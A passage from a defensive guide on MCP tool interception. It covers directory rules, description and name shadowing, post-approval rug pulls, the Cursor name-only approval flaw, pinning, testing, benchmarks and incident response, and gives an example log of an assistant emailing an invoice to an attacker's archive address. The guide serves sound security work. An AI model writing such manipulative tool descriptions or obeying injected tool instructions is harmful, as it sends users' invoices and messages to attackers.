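As of 23 October 2026, OpenAI's *Plugin guidelines* prohibit descriptions, titles, annotations and other model-readable fields "that manipulate how the model selects or uses other plugins or their tools". This covers both selection manipulation and description shadowing. OpenAI also bans promotional tool names, such as `pick_me` and `best`, and doesn't let a tool instruct the model to call another publisher's plugin.

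Under Anthropic's directory policy as of 6 August 2026, listed software "must not attempt to interfere with Claude calling tools from other software" unless the user wants it to. Anthropic also bans software that contains hidden instructions, coerces Claude into calling other tools, or has descriptions that create "confusion or conflict" with other listed software.

OpenAI's wording is clearer about persuasion, because its example of manipulation is telling the model to prefer one plugin. Anthropic's policy doesn't mention preference, although Anthropic's checklist for developers lists promoting products as a reason for rejection. The ban on confusion doesn't depend on the publisher's intent, so it could apply to a second `send_email` tool even if the tool's description contained no instructions.

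| | OpenAI | Anthropic |
|---|---|---|
| Scope | Plugins in the directory shared by ChatGPT and Codex | Connectors, skills, plugins and other software in Anthropic's directories |
| First review | Automated checks, then a review team | Automatic scan; staff test each tool only for the "Verified" label |
| Penalties | Rejection, restriction or removal, with a right of appeal | Refusal or removal at any time, for any reason |
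| Servers that users add themselves | Not covered | Not covered |

Anthropic lists connectors that pass the scan as "Community" by default. It may later select especially useful ones for the closer "Verified" review, but warns that even this review isn't a security audit.

OpenAI's reviewers work partly from tests that the publisher writes. OpenAI's *Upload and submit your plugin* requires a plugin with an MCP server to have five test cases in which it should act and three in which it shouldn't. The three negative cases for the page's sample notes plugin are transferring money, deleting all notes and reading another workspace. None is a request meant for another publisher's tool, such as finding an invoice, and a dishonest publisher is unlikely to include one.

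The penalties are mild for an attacker. Removing a tool from a directory stops new users from finding it there, but doesn't recover invoices the publisher has already collected. OpenAI also investigates user reports, but users may never notice that the wrong tool answered.

### Three descriptions of a notes tool

Suppose the notes developer submits `search_notes` with this description: "Searches the text of the user's meeting notes. Use it when the user asks about a past meeting." This satisfies both companies' rules because it explains what the tool does and when to use it, and doesn't mention any other tool.

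The developer then adds that `search_notes` is more reliable than accounting tools and that the model should try it first for invoices. The addition breaks OpenAI's rule because it steers the choice between publishers and disparages an alternative, and Anthropic's rule because it interferes with calls to `get_invoice`.

An honest but very broad description is harder to judge: "Searches the user's notes about meetings, people, decisions, payments and invoices. Use it whenever the user needs information." If people in the office do write about payments in their notes, the first sentence is true, but the second still conflicts with OpenAI's ban on "overly broad triggering" and Anthropic's requirement for narrow descriptions.

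If the developer deletes the second sentence, the remaining text probably complies with OpenAI's rules. An Anthropic reviewer could object that the remaining text conflicts with the accounts server, but could also accept it as accurate. The words "payments and invoices" may still raise the tool's retrieval score enough that retrieval leaves out a tool the request needs.

A reviewer can solve this without accusing anyone of manipulation. OpenAI requires descriptions to include relevant limitations, so the reviewer can ask for one more sentence: "Finds what people wrote about invoices, not the invoices themselves." People who want their notes can still find the tool easily, and the model has a reason to choose `get_invoice` for invoice 1042.

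### Changes after a directory's review

In May 2026, Anthropic's *Manage your listing after publishing* said developers could change a listed server's tools with "no resubmission" and that there was "no scheduled re-review". Claude would pick up the new tools at the next connection. A developer could therefore pass the review with a narrow description of `search_notes` and then replace it with the one that disparages accounting tools.

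This gap was still open on 1 December 2026. Anthropic had removed the sentence about scheduled re-review, but developers could still change a tool simply by deploying the change. A reviewer must approve edits to the tool names shown in the directory, but those edits affect only the listing. Anthropic's policy mentions "ongoing reviews", but the terms that developers accept include no obligation to monitor listed software. The page for developers describes no check that a changed tool must pass before Claude uses it. Anthropic treats its own plugins more strictly, scanning each new version and offering the old one until the new one passes.

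OpenAI used to require a new review for every change. When jbrodriguez asked in *How to surface mcp server updates for an existing plugin* why an edited description hadn't appeared in ChatGPT, an OpenAI employee explained that ChatGPT was using a stored snapshot from the review. To replace it, the developer had to submit a new version.

By November 2026, OpenAI had replaced this rule with what OpenAI's *Remote MCP server review requirements* calls continuous review. OpenAI scans each published server daily and compares its tools with the approved definitions. The two directories now treat changes to a listed MCP server as follows:

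| Change | OpenAI | Anthropic |
|---|---|---|
| New tool | Unavailable until it passes automated checks | Available once the developer deploys it |
| Changed description or parameters | The old definition stays in use until the new one passes | Takes effect once the developer deploys it |
| Deleted tool | Disappears after the next scan | Disappears once the developer deploys the change |
| New code behind the same definition | Takes effect immediately | Takes effect immediately |

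OpenAI's process gives better protection because the model doesn't receive the new text before the checks. It is weaker than the old rule in one respect, since an edited description now only has to pass automated checks and doesn't need a new submission. In tests by Dai and colleagues, automated detectors missed nearly all of the subtler manipulative descriptions, so the office can't rely on either directory to catch a well-written change.

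### Approval by name: the Cursor flaw

Most post-approval changes are ordinary updates, not malicious rug pulls. Kraishan found that 51.1% of the 8,900 servers with more than one version in the official MCP Registry had changed their registry description, packages or addresses. Among those, the median time to the first change was less than a day.

Kraishan classified changes at 40.6% of the 8,900 servers as silent, meaning that the server's identifiers stayed the same. For most of these servers, only the wording of the description had changed. More seriously, 370 had moved to a different host under the same registry name. Most of the moves were probably routine, but neither the registry nor a client can distinguish a move by the owner from a takeover.

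A flaw in Cursor shows how an attacker can exploit an approval that covers only a name. A software project can include a configuration file that lists MCP servers, with a name and a start command for each. Cursor asked the user to approve each entry once. Charikov, Zaikin and Vanunu (2025), in *CVE-2025-54136*, showed that Cursor then remembered only the name:

1. Someone who can edit a shared project adds an entry with a harmless command.
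2. A colleague opens the project and approves the entry.
3. The attacker keeps the name but changes the command.
4. Cursor runs the new command on the colleague's computer without asking, and does so again whenever the project opens.

INCIBE's *CVE-2025-54136* (2025) lists Cursor version 1.2.4 and earlier as affected. The researchers reported the flaw on 16 July 2025, and Cursor released version 1.3 on 29 July. The release notes didn't mention the problem, but the researchers confirmed the fix through testing. Cursor now asks for approval again after any change to the entry, even an added space.

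That fix covers the command that starts a server, but not the tool definitions the server later supplies. *SchemaCaps* (Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee, 2026) examined how eight clients, programming libraries and scanners handle changed definitions. In the middle of a session, the test server removed a restriction on a file-reading tool's input and added a field for an outside web address, but left the tool's name and description unchanged.

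Six of the eight products didn't ask for new approval when a tool's definition changed. The researchers couldn't determine what the other two, Cursor and Claude Desktop, do. VS Code keeps the earlier approval because it identifies tools by name, and Claude Code's permission rules also match names. The researchers ran only four of the eight products, and their finding for Claude Code comes from its documentation, so an administrator should test the client the office uses.

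### Pinning a definition

*Pinning* ties an approval to the exact content of a definition. The client records the approved version and refuses any other until someone approves it. For `search_notes`, this takes six steps.

**1. The client collects everything the model can read.** This covers the tool's name, title, description, input and output schemas, annotations and any other fields. It should also cover the server's general instructions if the client passes them to the model. The scanner mcp-scan used to compare only descriptions, so it missed the change in Ameur and colleagues' test. Later versions dropped pinning.

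**2. Put the definition in a standard form.** A server might send the same fields in a different order or with different spacing. The client sorts the field names, removes spaces between fields and uses one character encoding. It leaves the wording of the description alone, because any change there could affect the model. With the schema left out for brevity, the result looks like this:

```
Received:   { "name": "search_notes",
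              "description": "Searches saved notes. Use for questions about meetings." }

Standard:   {"description":"Searches saved notes. Use for questions about meetings.","name":"search_notes"}
```

**3. Calculate a hash.** SHA-256, a widely used hash function, turns text of any length into a 64-character code. A small change to the text produces a completely different code. For example, the hash of "The quick brown fox jumps over the lazy dog" begins with `d7a8fbb3`, but changing "dog" to "cog" produces a hash that begins with `e4c4d8f3`.

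**4. The client should store the hash with the server's identity.** The record needs the server's address and its identifier from the client's own configuration. For a server on the user's computer, the start command and a hash of the package replace the address. Otherwise, a different server could supply an identical definition and inherit the approval. The client should also keep the full approved text, because it can't reconstruct the text from the hash.

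**5. Compare at every listing.** The client repeats steps 1 to 3 whenever it fetches the list of tools, not just at start-up. *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (Lee, Chang and colleagues, 2026) demonstrated that scripts can replace tools on web pages during a session, so those tools need this too. A tool with no stored hash is new and needs its own approval.

**6. Block the tool and show the difference.** Suppose the notes developer changes one word in the description. With invented hashes, shortened to eight characters, the administrator might see this:

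```
Server:     notes (example.notes/notes-server)
Tool:       search_notes

Approved:   Use for questions about meetings.     hash 5c1e90ab
Received:   Use for questions about invoices.     hash e27f4d38
```

Until someone approves the change, the client must keep the new definition out of the model's context. Refusing calls to `search_notes` isn't enough, because description shadowing works even if the tool is never called. The client can keep using the server's unchanged tools, but it should suspend all of the server's tools if the server's address changes. The text a person approves can differ from the text the model reads, so the client should display and hash exactly what it passes to the model.

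Ameur and colleagues built a program that sits between the client and the server and can do most of this. It hides changed tools from the model, blocks calls to them, and suspends every tool if the server's identity changes. It added about half a millisecond to each call.

### What the 2026 specification adds

The protocol revision of 28 July 2026 makes comparisons easier, although its authors introduced the relevant rules mainly to save time and computing costs. Model Context Protocol's list of changes includes four that matter here:

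| Change | Use for pinning |
|---|---|
| A server's tool list no longer varies between connections | Two computers in the office can compare their lists, and an unexplained difference deserves investigation |
| Servers should return tools in a consistent order | A hash of the whole list doesn't change just because the order did |
| Each list includes a time, `ttlMs`, for which clients may treat it as fresh | The client has a suggested time for its next comparison |
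| Clients can subscribe to notifications of changed lists | The client can compare soon after an honest server announces an update |

For example, a server can set `ttlMs` to 3,600,000 milliseconds to suggest that the client can reuse the list for an hour. The server chooses that number, so the office should set its own maximum. A malicious server can also ignore the rule about consistent lists. The revision doesn't add a hash or signature to tool definitions, so clients still have to pin the definitions themselves.

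### Signed definitions

Pinning reveals that a definition has changed but not who changed it. Bhatt, Narajala and Habler (2025), in *ETDI*, propose that publishers sign their definitions. The publisher signs each definition with a private key and gives clients the matching public one. The signed definition includes a version number and the permissions that the tool needs. A client handles it in four steps:

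1. It checks the signature and rejects the tool if the check fails.
2. It compares the version and hash with those the user approved before.
3. It asks for approval if the tool is new, if the version is newer, or if the content differs under the same version number.
4. It stores the new version, hash and permissions.

If someone breaks into the notes server but doesn't have the developer's private key, they can't produce a valid signature for a changed description. The dishonest developer can sign one, and the attack then works unless the user notices the problem when asked to approve the new version. Clients also need a safe way to get the right public key. ETDI suggests including keys with the application or using a trusted key registry.

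The sample procedure doesn't block older versions of a tool definition by default. It logs a warning and leaves the operator to decide what to do. If the operator adds no rule, the procedure stores the older version as approved. An attacker who controls the server could then bring back an old signed definition, such as one the developer withdrew because of a mistake. A client should refuse older versions unless an administrator requests them.

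Bhatt and colleagues also suggest that the definition include a hash of the tool's *API contract*, a formal description of the requests that the publisher's service accepts. A change to the contract would then require a new version. The hash doesn't cover the service's code. In the paper's example of a rug pull, a wallpaper tool keeps its version number while new code searches the user's documents. ETDI wouldn't detect that change if the definition and the contract stayed the same. The researchers published a working implementation but no measurements of how well it protects users.

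### The burden of repeated approvals

Pinning can produce more approval requests than people will read. Ameur and colleagues compared 604 releases of 39 MCP servers, published between January 2025 and September 2026. Pinning complete definitions would have required 2,004 new approvals for existing tools, an average of 51 per server. The sample included at most 20 releases of each server, so a server that updates often could require many more.

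One proposal is to ask for approval only when a new schema allows something that the old one didn't. For example, an update to Desktop Commander, a server that runs commands on the user's computer, kept every old call working but also let the model choose which shell program would run the commands. Browsers apply a similar rule when they disable an extension whose update adds a permission. The proposed rule would have triggered 645 approval requests.

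For interception, the saving has a serious drawback, because the rule ignores descriptions. It would let the notes developer replace "meetings" with "invoices" without any question. Changes to descriptions or titles alone accounted for 807 of the 2,004 approvals, and those are exactly the changes that can redirect requests. The office should therefore pin the complete definition and reduce the number of questions in other ways:

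- **Ask once per release.** The study compared 565 pairs of successive releases, so showing all of a release's changes together would have meant at most 565 questions about existing tools.
- **Let one administrator decide for everyone.** The administrator knows what the server is for, and other employees don't have to judge the same change again.
- **Choose when to update.** The office can keep a server on its own computers at an approved version and review several months of changes together. The drawback is that security fixes also wait, so the administrator has to watch for urgent ones.

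*Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (2026), an 89-day study of registry descriptions, found that checking only the servers that changed often in the past misses changes. It recommends tying approval to the content and also checking all servers periodically.

### Code behind an unchanged definition

A hash of a tool definition doesn't cover the tool's code. In Ameur and colleagues' simulated attacks, a server that changed its behaviour but kept the same schema got past every rule, including pinning. OpenAI's directory has the same limit, because OpenAI stores the approved definition but not a copy of the server's code.

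If the server runs on the office's own computers, the administrator can also pin its package. An office that had pinned a harmless version of `postmark-mcp` would have kept using that version, and a reviewer comparing it with the malicious update would have had only one new line to read. Pinning the package works only if the program doesn't download more code after installation.

The code of a remote server stays on the publisher's computers, so the office can only observe the server's behavior. *ProbeID* (2026) checks a tool by sending it fixed requests and comparing the answers with earlier ones. In a simulated rug pull, blocking tools that failed the comparison reduced corrupted calls from 93 of 1,575 to 20 of 1,323. The study also found tools whose answers changed while the server's version number stayed the same.

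A changed answer doesn't always mean an attack. One tool in the study reported current conditions, so its answers varied, and another changed because of something on the researchers' computer. The method suits tools whose answers should stay the same. For example, the office could keep a test invoice in its accounts system and regularly check that `get_invoice` returns the same amount and bank account number. These requests should look like ordinary ones, because a malicious server that detects a test can return the right answer for it and still return a false one for invoice 1042.

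## Testing a system for interception and recognising it in logs

An office can check its protections by adding its own harmless tool and counting how many requests the tool diverts. The test should run in a copy of the assistant, with invented invoices and a mail server that delivers nothing. The test tool only records each call and returns a fixed answer.

### A test for the office assistant

1. **List every tool and its server.** The tester should take this list from the text that the client passes to the model, because the configuration may not match it. Ahmed and Abbas (2026), in *Labels Are Not Endpoints*, audited their own earlier experiment and found that one set of planned attack texts had never reached the models. Prompts labelled with different defences had also been identical.
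2. **Write requests for each sensitive task.** For the office, these tasks are looking up invoices and sending email. The requests should vary in the invoice, the person, the purpose and the wording, and should not name a tool. The tester writes down the correct server, tool and arguments for each request in advance.
3. **Run the requests without the test tool.** This shows how often the assistant makes ordinary mistakes.
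4. **Add the test tool in several versions**, one at a time, as in the table below.
5. **Rotate the order.** The test tool should come before the genuine one in half the runs and after it in the other half.
6. **Repeat every request** a few times in fresh sessions, because a model may choose differently on another attempt.

| Version of the test tool | What it tests |
|---|---|
| Same name as the genuine tool, `send_email` | Whether the client keeps duplicate names apart |
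| Neutral copy with a different name and the same description | How the model chooses between equivalent tools |
| Broader description that also mentions invoices and payments | Whether wording alone attracts requests |
| Description with a harmless rule for emails, such as ending each one with a certain word | Whether one tool's description changes calls to another |

The tester should count wrong tools and altered arguments separately, because they need different defences:

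```
wrong-tool rate        =  runs in which the test tool received a call            /  all runs
altered-argument rate  =  runs in which the right tool received wrong arguments  /  all runs
```

If the assistant calls both the test tool and the genuine one, the run still counts towards the first rate, because a malicious tool would have received the data. *When Tool Names Are Not Identities* (2026) uses a similar count and allows for two other outcomes, in which the client asks for clarification or fails. These need their own column. In Ahmed and Abbas's experiment, 84 of 180 distinct requests produced no usable result, including all 45 for one model. Such failures don't show that a model resisted interception.

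A program that counts attacks must not use information about which version of the test tool was present. Ahmed and Abbas's original program did, and it classified the results of 70 distinct requests as successful or attempted attacks, though 58 of them turned out to be ordinary, authorised work. A tester can check for this mistake by giving the program the same record labelled with a different version of the tool and confirming that the verdict stays the same.

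The test is fairly cheap. *COPEX* (Birhan, Rostamzadeh and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark of attacks on MCP systems, reports costs of $2.77 to $21.53 for 375 runs on each commercial model. At those prices, running 300 requests once without the test tool and once with each of its four versions, 1,500 runs in total, would cost about $11 to $86 per model.

### What the counts can prove

Suppose the test tool diverts none of 300 independent requests. If its true rate of diversion were p, the chance of this result would be (1 − p)^300. The 95% upper bound is the value of p at which that chance falls to 5%:

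```
(1 − p)^300 = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) = 0.0099, or about 1%
```

A system that gets a perfect test score could still have a true interception rate of up to about 1%. At that rate, an office that handles 2,000 invoice requests a month would have about 20 of them intercepted.

If the version with the broader description diverts 12 of 300 requests, the measured rate is 4%, with a 95% Wilson confidence interval of 2.3% to 6.9%.

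To find out whether a defence helps, the tester should run the same requests before and after adding it and compare the results request by request. Suppose 12 requests were diverted before the defence was added. Afterwards, 10 of those reach the right tool, two still go wrong, and one other request that used to work fails. Eleven results changed, ten for the better. If the defence had no effect, a split at least this uneven would occur by chance only 1.2% of the time. This calculation is McNemar's test, which *TrustShiftProbe* (2026), a study of servers that attack after gaining trust, uses to evaluate its defence.

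These calculations assume that the requests are independent, and rewordings of one request are not. "Find invoice 1042", "get me invoice 1042" and "I need invoice 1042" share nearly everything that could attract or repel the model, so if one goes to the right tool, the others probably will too. Suppose the 300 requests consist of 30 situations with 10 wordings each, and ρ measures how alike the wordings of one situation behave, from 0 (unrelated) to 1 (identical). The effective number of requests is:

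```
n_eff = 300 / (1 + (10 − 1) · ρ)
```

| ρ | Effective number of requests | Upper bound after no diversions |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 300 | 1.0% |
| 0.5 | 55 | 5.3% |
| 1 | 30 | 9.5% |

A test without any diversions gives no information about ρ, so the last row is the cautious choice. Adding 30 situations will improve the test more than adding 300 wordings, and repeating identical requests will help even less. Ahmed and Abbas recorded 10,200 runs, but their models always gave the same answer to the same input, so the runs contained only 180 distinct requests built from 15 underlying tasks.

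Even without statistical error, a pass applies only to the descriptions tested. An attacker can try many wordings on a replica and publish the best one, as Dai and colleagues did. Suppose one wording in 200 would capture most invoice requests. A tester who tries a single wording has a 99.5% chance of missing the weakness, while an attacker who tries 500 has a 92% chance of finding it. A pass is therefore only weak evidence that the system is safe, even though a failure is strong evidence of a problem.

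The office can be more confident about protections that don't depend on the model's judgement. If fixed routing is supposed to keep the notes server out of invoice sessions, the tester can check whether the server's definitions ever appear in the model's context during those sessions.

### What published benchmarks found

Three benchmarks measured how well systems resist false tools with familiar names. *MCPSecBench* (Yang, Gao and colleagues, 2025) tested whole applications. Its February 2026 version covers Cursor, OpenAI's GPT-4.1, and Claude Desktop with Claude Opus 4.5, and runs each attack 15 times.

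In *MCP Security Bench (MSB)*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2025) tested ten models from 2024 and 2025, including GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4, on 2,000 test cases with working tools. Birhan and colleagues wrote five scenarios for each of 25 attacks and ran each scenario three times. They tested nine models, including Claude Opus 4.7, GPT-5.5, Gemini 3.1 and Grok 4.3 (all available by May 2026), inside the same surrounding software.

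| Benchmark | System | Similar tool name | Similar server name | "Tool shadowing" |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Yang and colleagues | Claude Desktop | 100% | 100% | 20% |
| Yang and colleagues | GPT-4.1 | 100% | 100% | 53.3% |
| Yang and colleagues | Cursor | 100% | 100% | 6.7% |
| Zhang and colleagues | Average of ten models | 14.6% | – | – |
| Birhan and colleagues | Average of nine models | 58.5% | 94.8% | 0.7% |

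Much of the variation comes from how the researchers defined success. Zhang and colleagues named their false tool by adding `_v1` to a genuine tool's name. When the model called the false tool, the tool returned a fake error message containing a harmful instruction, and the attack counted as a success only if the model carried out that instruction. GPT-5 never did, but it may still have called the false tool.

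In the tests with promotional descriptions, the attack success rate for GPT-5 was 1.25% when success meant obeying the fake error message and 86.25% when it meant filling in an unnecessary parameter. The lower figure would falsely reassure an office worried about who receives its invoices, because the call itself already does the damage.

Birhan and colleagues compared two ways of scoring interception through similar tool names on four models. A program that checked whether the model had called the false tool gave 60% for every model, while a language model that judged the whole run gave 100%. In the main test, eight of the nine models also scored exactly 60%. Most likely, three of the five scenarios worked on nearly every model and the other two didn't, so the figure reflects the choice of scenarios more than differences between models.

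The benchmarks also use the term "tool shadowing" for different attacks. In Yang and colleagues' test, a false tool ran after a genuine one and altered its result, much like `format_invoice`. Cursor's low rate came from a limit on calling several tools in a row, and the researchers found no sign that it had detected the attack. Birhan and colleagues describe a server that registers tools to shadow legitimate ones, which seems closer to name shadowing. Their attack succeeded once in 135 runs. One of their published records has the server's name in front of the tool's name, so prefixes may have prevented most collisions.

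*MCP-SafetyBench* (Zong, Shen and colleagues, 2025) uses "tool shadowing" for tools that change how other tools behave. The benchmark has 245 cases and checks separately whether the user's task succeeded and whether the attack did. In one example, a user asks about Johnson & Johnson shares, but a poisoned tool definition changes the stock symbol to Tesla's.

In Birhan and colleagues' results, the category closest to description shadowing is probably "parameter poisoning", in which tool descriptions redirect or modify what the user asked for. It succeeded in 43% of runs on average, but the rate ranged from 0% for Claude Opus 4.7 to 100% for Gemini 3.1, so an office can't infer much about its own model from the average.

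Model rankings also change with the attack. Among the six models in *TrustShiftProbe*, Claude Opus 4.8 had the lowest attack success rate for "dependency hijack", at 27.5%, and the highest for "cross-tool lateral movement", at 54.8%.

Yang and colleagues' perfect scores for similar tool names should be read with some caution, because with 15 successes in 15 runs the true rate could still be as low as 82%. They also published an example in which Cursor had two tools with identical descriptions and picked the genuine one, and its output described the choice as arbitrary. If Cursor chose at random, it would pick the false tool in all 15 runs only once in about 33,000 tests. It may instead have favoured one position in the list, so an operator's own test should rotate the order of the tools. The gap between Claude Desktop and GPT-4.1 on tool shadowing could also be chance, since their 95% intervals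 overlap (7% to 45% and 30% to 75%).

Researchers disagree about whether the model or the surrounding application matters more. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* concludes from its test of seven client applications that the application matters more. *Weighing the Envelope* (2026) cites a study in which the surrounding software explained only 0.5% of the variation in results. The office should therefore repeat its test whenever the model or the application changes.

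### What to record

A log that contains only tool names can't distinguish the mail server's `send_email` from an impostor's. A useful record of a call might look like this, with invented hashes:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-04T14:07:31Z",
  "session": "a83f",
  "request": "find invoice 1042 and send it to Dana",
  "model_version": "model-2026-11",
  "tools_offered": [
    { "server": "accounts", "tool": "get_invoice",  "hash": "5b20c7e1" },
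    { "server": "mail",     "tool": "send_email",   "hash": "91d4ae06" },
    { "server": "notes",    "tool": "search_notes", "hash": "c30b7f52" }
  ],
  "call": {
    "server": "mail",
    "address": "https://mcp.mail.example",
    "tool": "send_email",
    "arguments": { "to": "archive@notes.example", "body": "invoice 1042" }
  },
  "result": "sent"
}
```

- **Server identity.** The identifier should come from the client's own configuration, along with the address that the client actually contacted.
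- **Definition hash.** This shows which version of the definition the model received. The office needs to keep the full text of each version elsewhere.
- **Arguments.** The client should log exactly what it sends, not the model's summary of it.
- **Tools on offer.** In this example, the false archive rule is in the description of `search_notes`, which the assistant never called. A list of calls alone would give no clue to the cause. The full list also shows whether a retriever left out the genuine tool.

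Such logs contain invoices, addresses and private messages, so few people should have access, and the office should delete old records on a fixed schedule. No tool server should be able to read or edit the logs. The client must also remove passwords and access tokens before saving a record. In Birhan and colleagues' benchmark, attacks that exposed tokens through logs or error messages succeeded in 67.4% of runs.

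The client's log can't show what a server does with data after receiving it, so it would have missed the copies that `postmark-mcp` sent.

### Warning signs and their innocent causes

The clearest sign of interception is a sudden shift of one task's calls to a different server. Suppose the assistant makes 10,000 calls a week, 200 of them to look up invoices, and the notes server starts receiving 60 of those 200. Those 60 are 0.6% of all calls but 30% of invoice lookups, so the office should count calls separately for each sensitive task.

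| Sign | Possible attack | Innocent cause |
|---|---|---|
| One task's calls move to another server | Name shadowing or selection manipulation | A planned change of server, a new model version or an outage |
| Emails from several users go to the same unfamiliar address | Description shadowing | A new customer or supplier |
| A new tool runs before or after a trusted one | An inserted tool such as `format_invoice` | A new feature |
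| A genuine tool disappears from the tools on offer | A rival description that crowds it out | A change to the retriever or a disconnected server |
| A definition's hash changes | Post-approval change | An ordinary update |
| More tasks fail or need repeating | A false tool that doesn't do the job | A fault in the genuine service |

Failed tasks can be quite a strong sign of interception. When Lee and colleagues replaced a web page's tool with a malicious one of the same name before the session began, all three models tested called the malicious tool every time and completed only 17% of their tasks. A competent attacker would avoid this by returning plausible results.

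Changes in how people phrase requests can also change which tools a model calls, even without an attacker. Al-Masri and Yang (2026), in *ShadowBench-MCP*, added phrases such as "use the fastest path" to ordinary requests. The model switched to a riskier sequence of tools in 14 of 48 comparisons when its instructions favoured efficiency, and in 2 of 48 when they required safety checks. The study used only one model and six tasks, but it suggests that a period of rushed requests, such as the end of the financial year, could look like an attack in the logs.

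To find the cause, the administrator can first compare the date of the shift with recent updates to the model, client and servers, then replay some of the affected requests in the test copy with and without the suspected notes server's definitions. If calls return to the accounts server only when those definitions are absent, the definitions caused the shift. An honest but overly broad description could have the same effect, so someone has to read the definitions to judge whether they are malicious.

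Comparing calls with past behaviour misses an attack that began the day the office installed the assistant, so the office should also compare each call with a list of which server is supposed to handle which task. Any invoice lookup on the notes server then raises an alert, even if such lookups have happened every day for a year.

### Responding to an interception

Suppose an alert leads the administrator to the record above, in which the assistant sent invoice 1042 to the archive address. The hash of `search_notes` doesn't match the approved version. The office can respond in four steps:

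1. **Disconnect the notes server.** The administrator saves a copy of its current definitions and package as evidence, blocks the server on every client, and ends all sessions that still have its tool descriptions in their context. The administrator also checks the assistant's long-term memory for text from the server.
2. **Revoke credentials.** This covers the notes server's own tokens and any password or token that appeared in an affected session or in a file the server could read. The office issues replacements only after disconnecting the server, or the attacker could collect those too.
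3. **Find the affected requests.** The administrator searches the logs for the hash of the bad definition among the tools on offer. A search for calls to the notes server would miss the altered emails, because those calls went to the mail server.
4. **Restore the approved definitions.** The administrator reloads the stored text, checks its hash and reruns the test before anyone uses the assistant for invoices again.

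The third step usually takes the most work. Suppose the bad definition was available in 412 sessions. In 37 of them, the assistant called a notes tool, so the office lists everything in the arguments of those calls as disclosed. Someone also compares the emails and other sensitive calls in all 412 sessions with the users' requests. If nine invoices went to the archive address, the office has to inform the people concerned, send the invoices to the right recipients and find out whether data protection law requires a report.

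The administrator also checks the bank account numbers on invoices sent during that period against those in the accounts system. A false number could lead a customer to pay the attacker weeks later, so a quick call to the customer may prevent the largest loss.

Restoring a tool's definition doesn't restore its code. If the notes server runs on the office's computers, the administrator can reinstall the approved package. If it runs on the developer's computers, the office can't tell what else has changed, so it should keep the server disconnected until the developer explains the incident and the server passes a new review. The administrator should also report the server to the registry that lists it and add the affected requests to the office's regular test.
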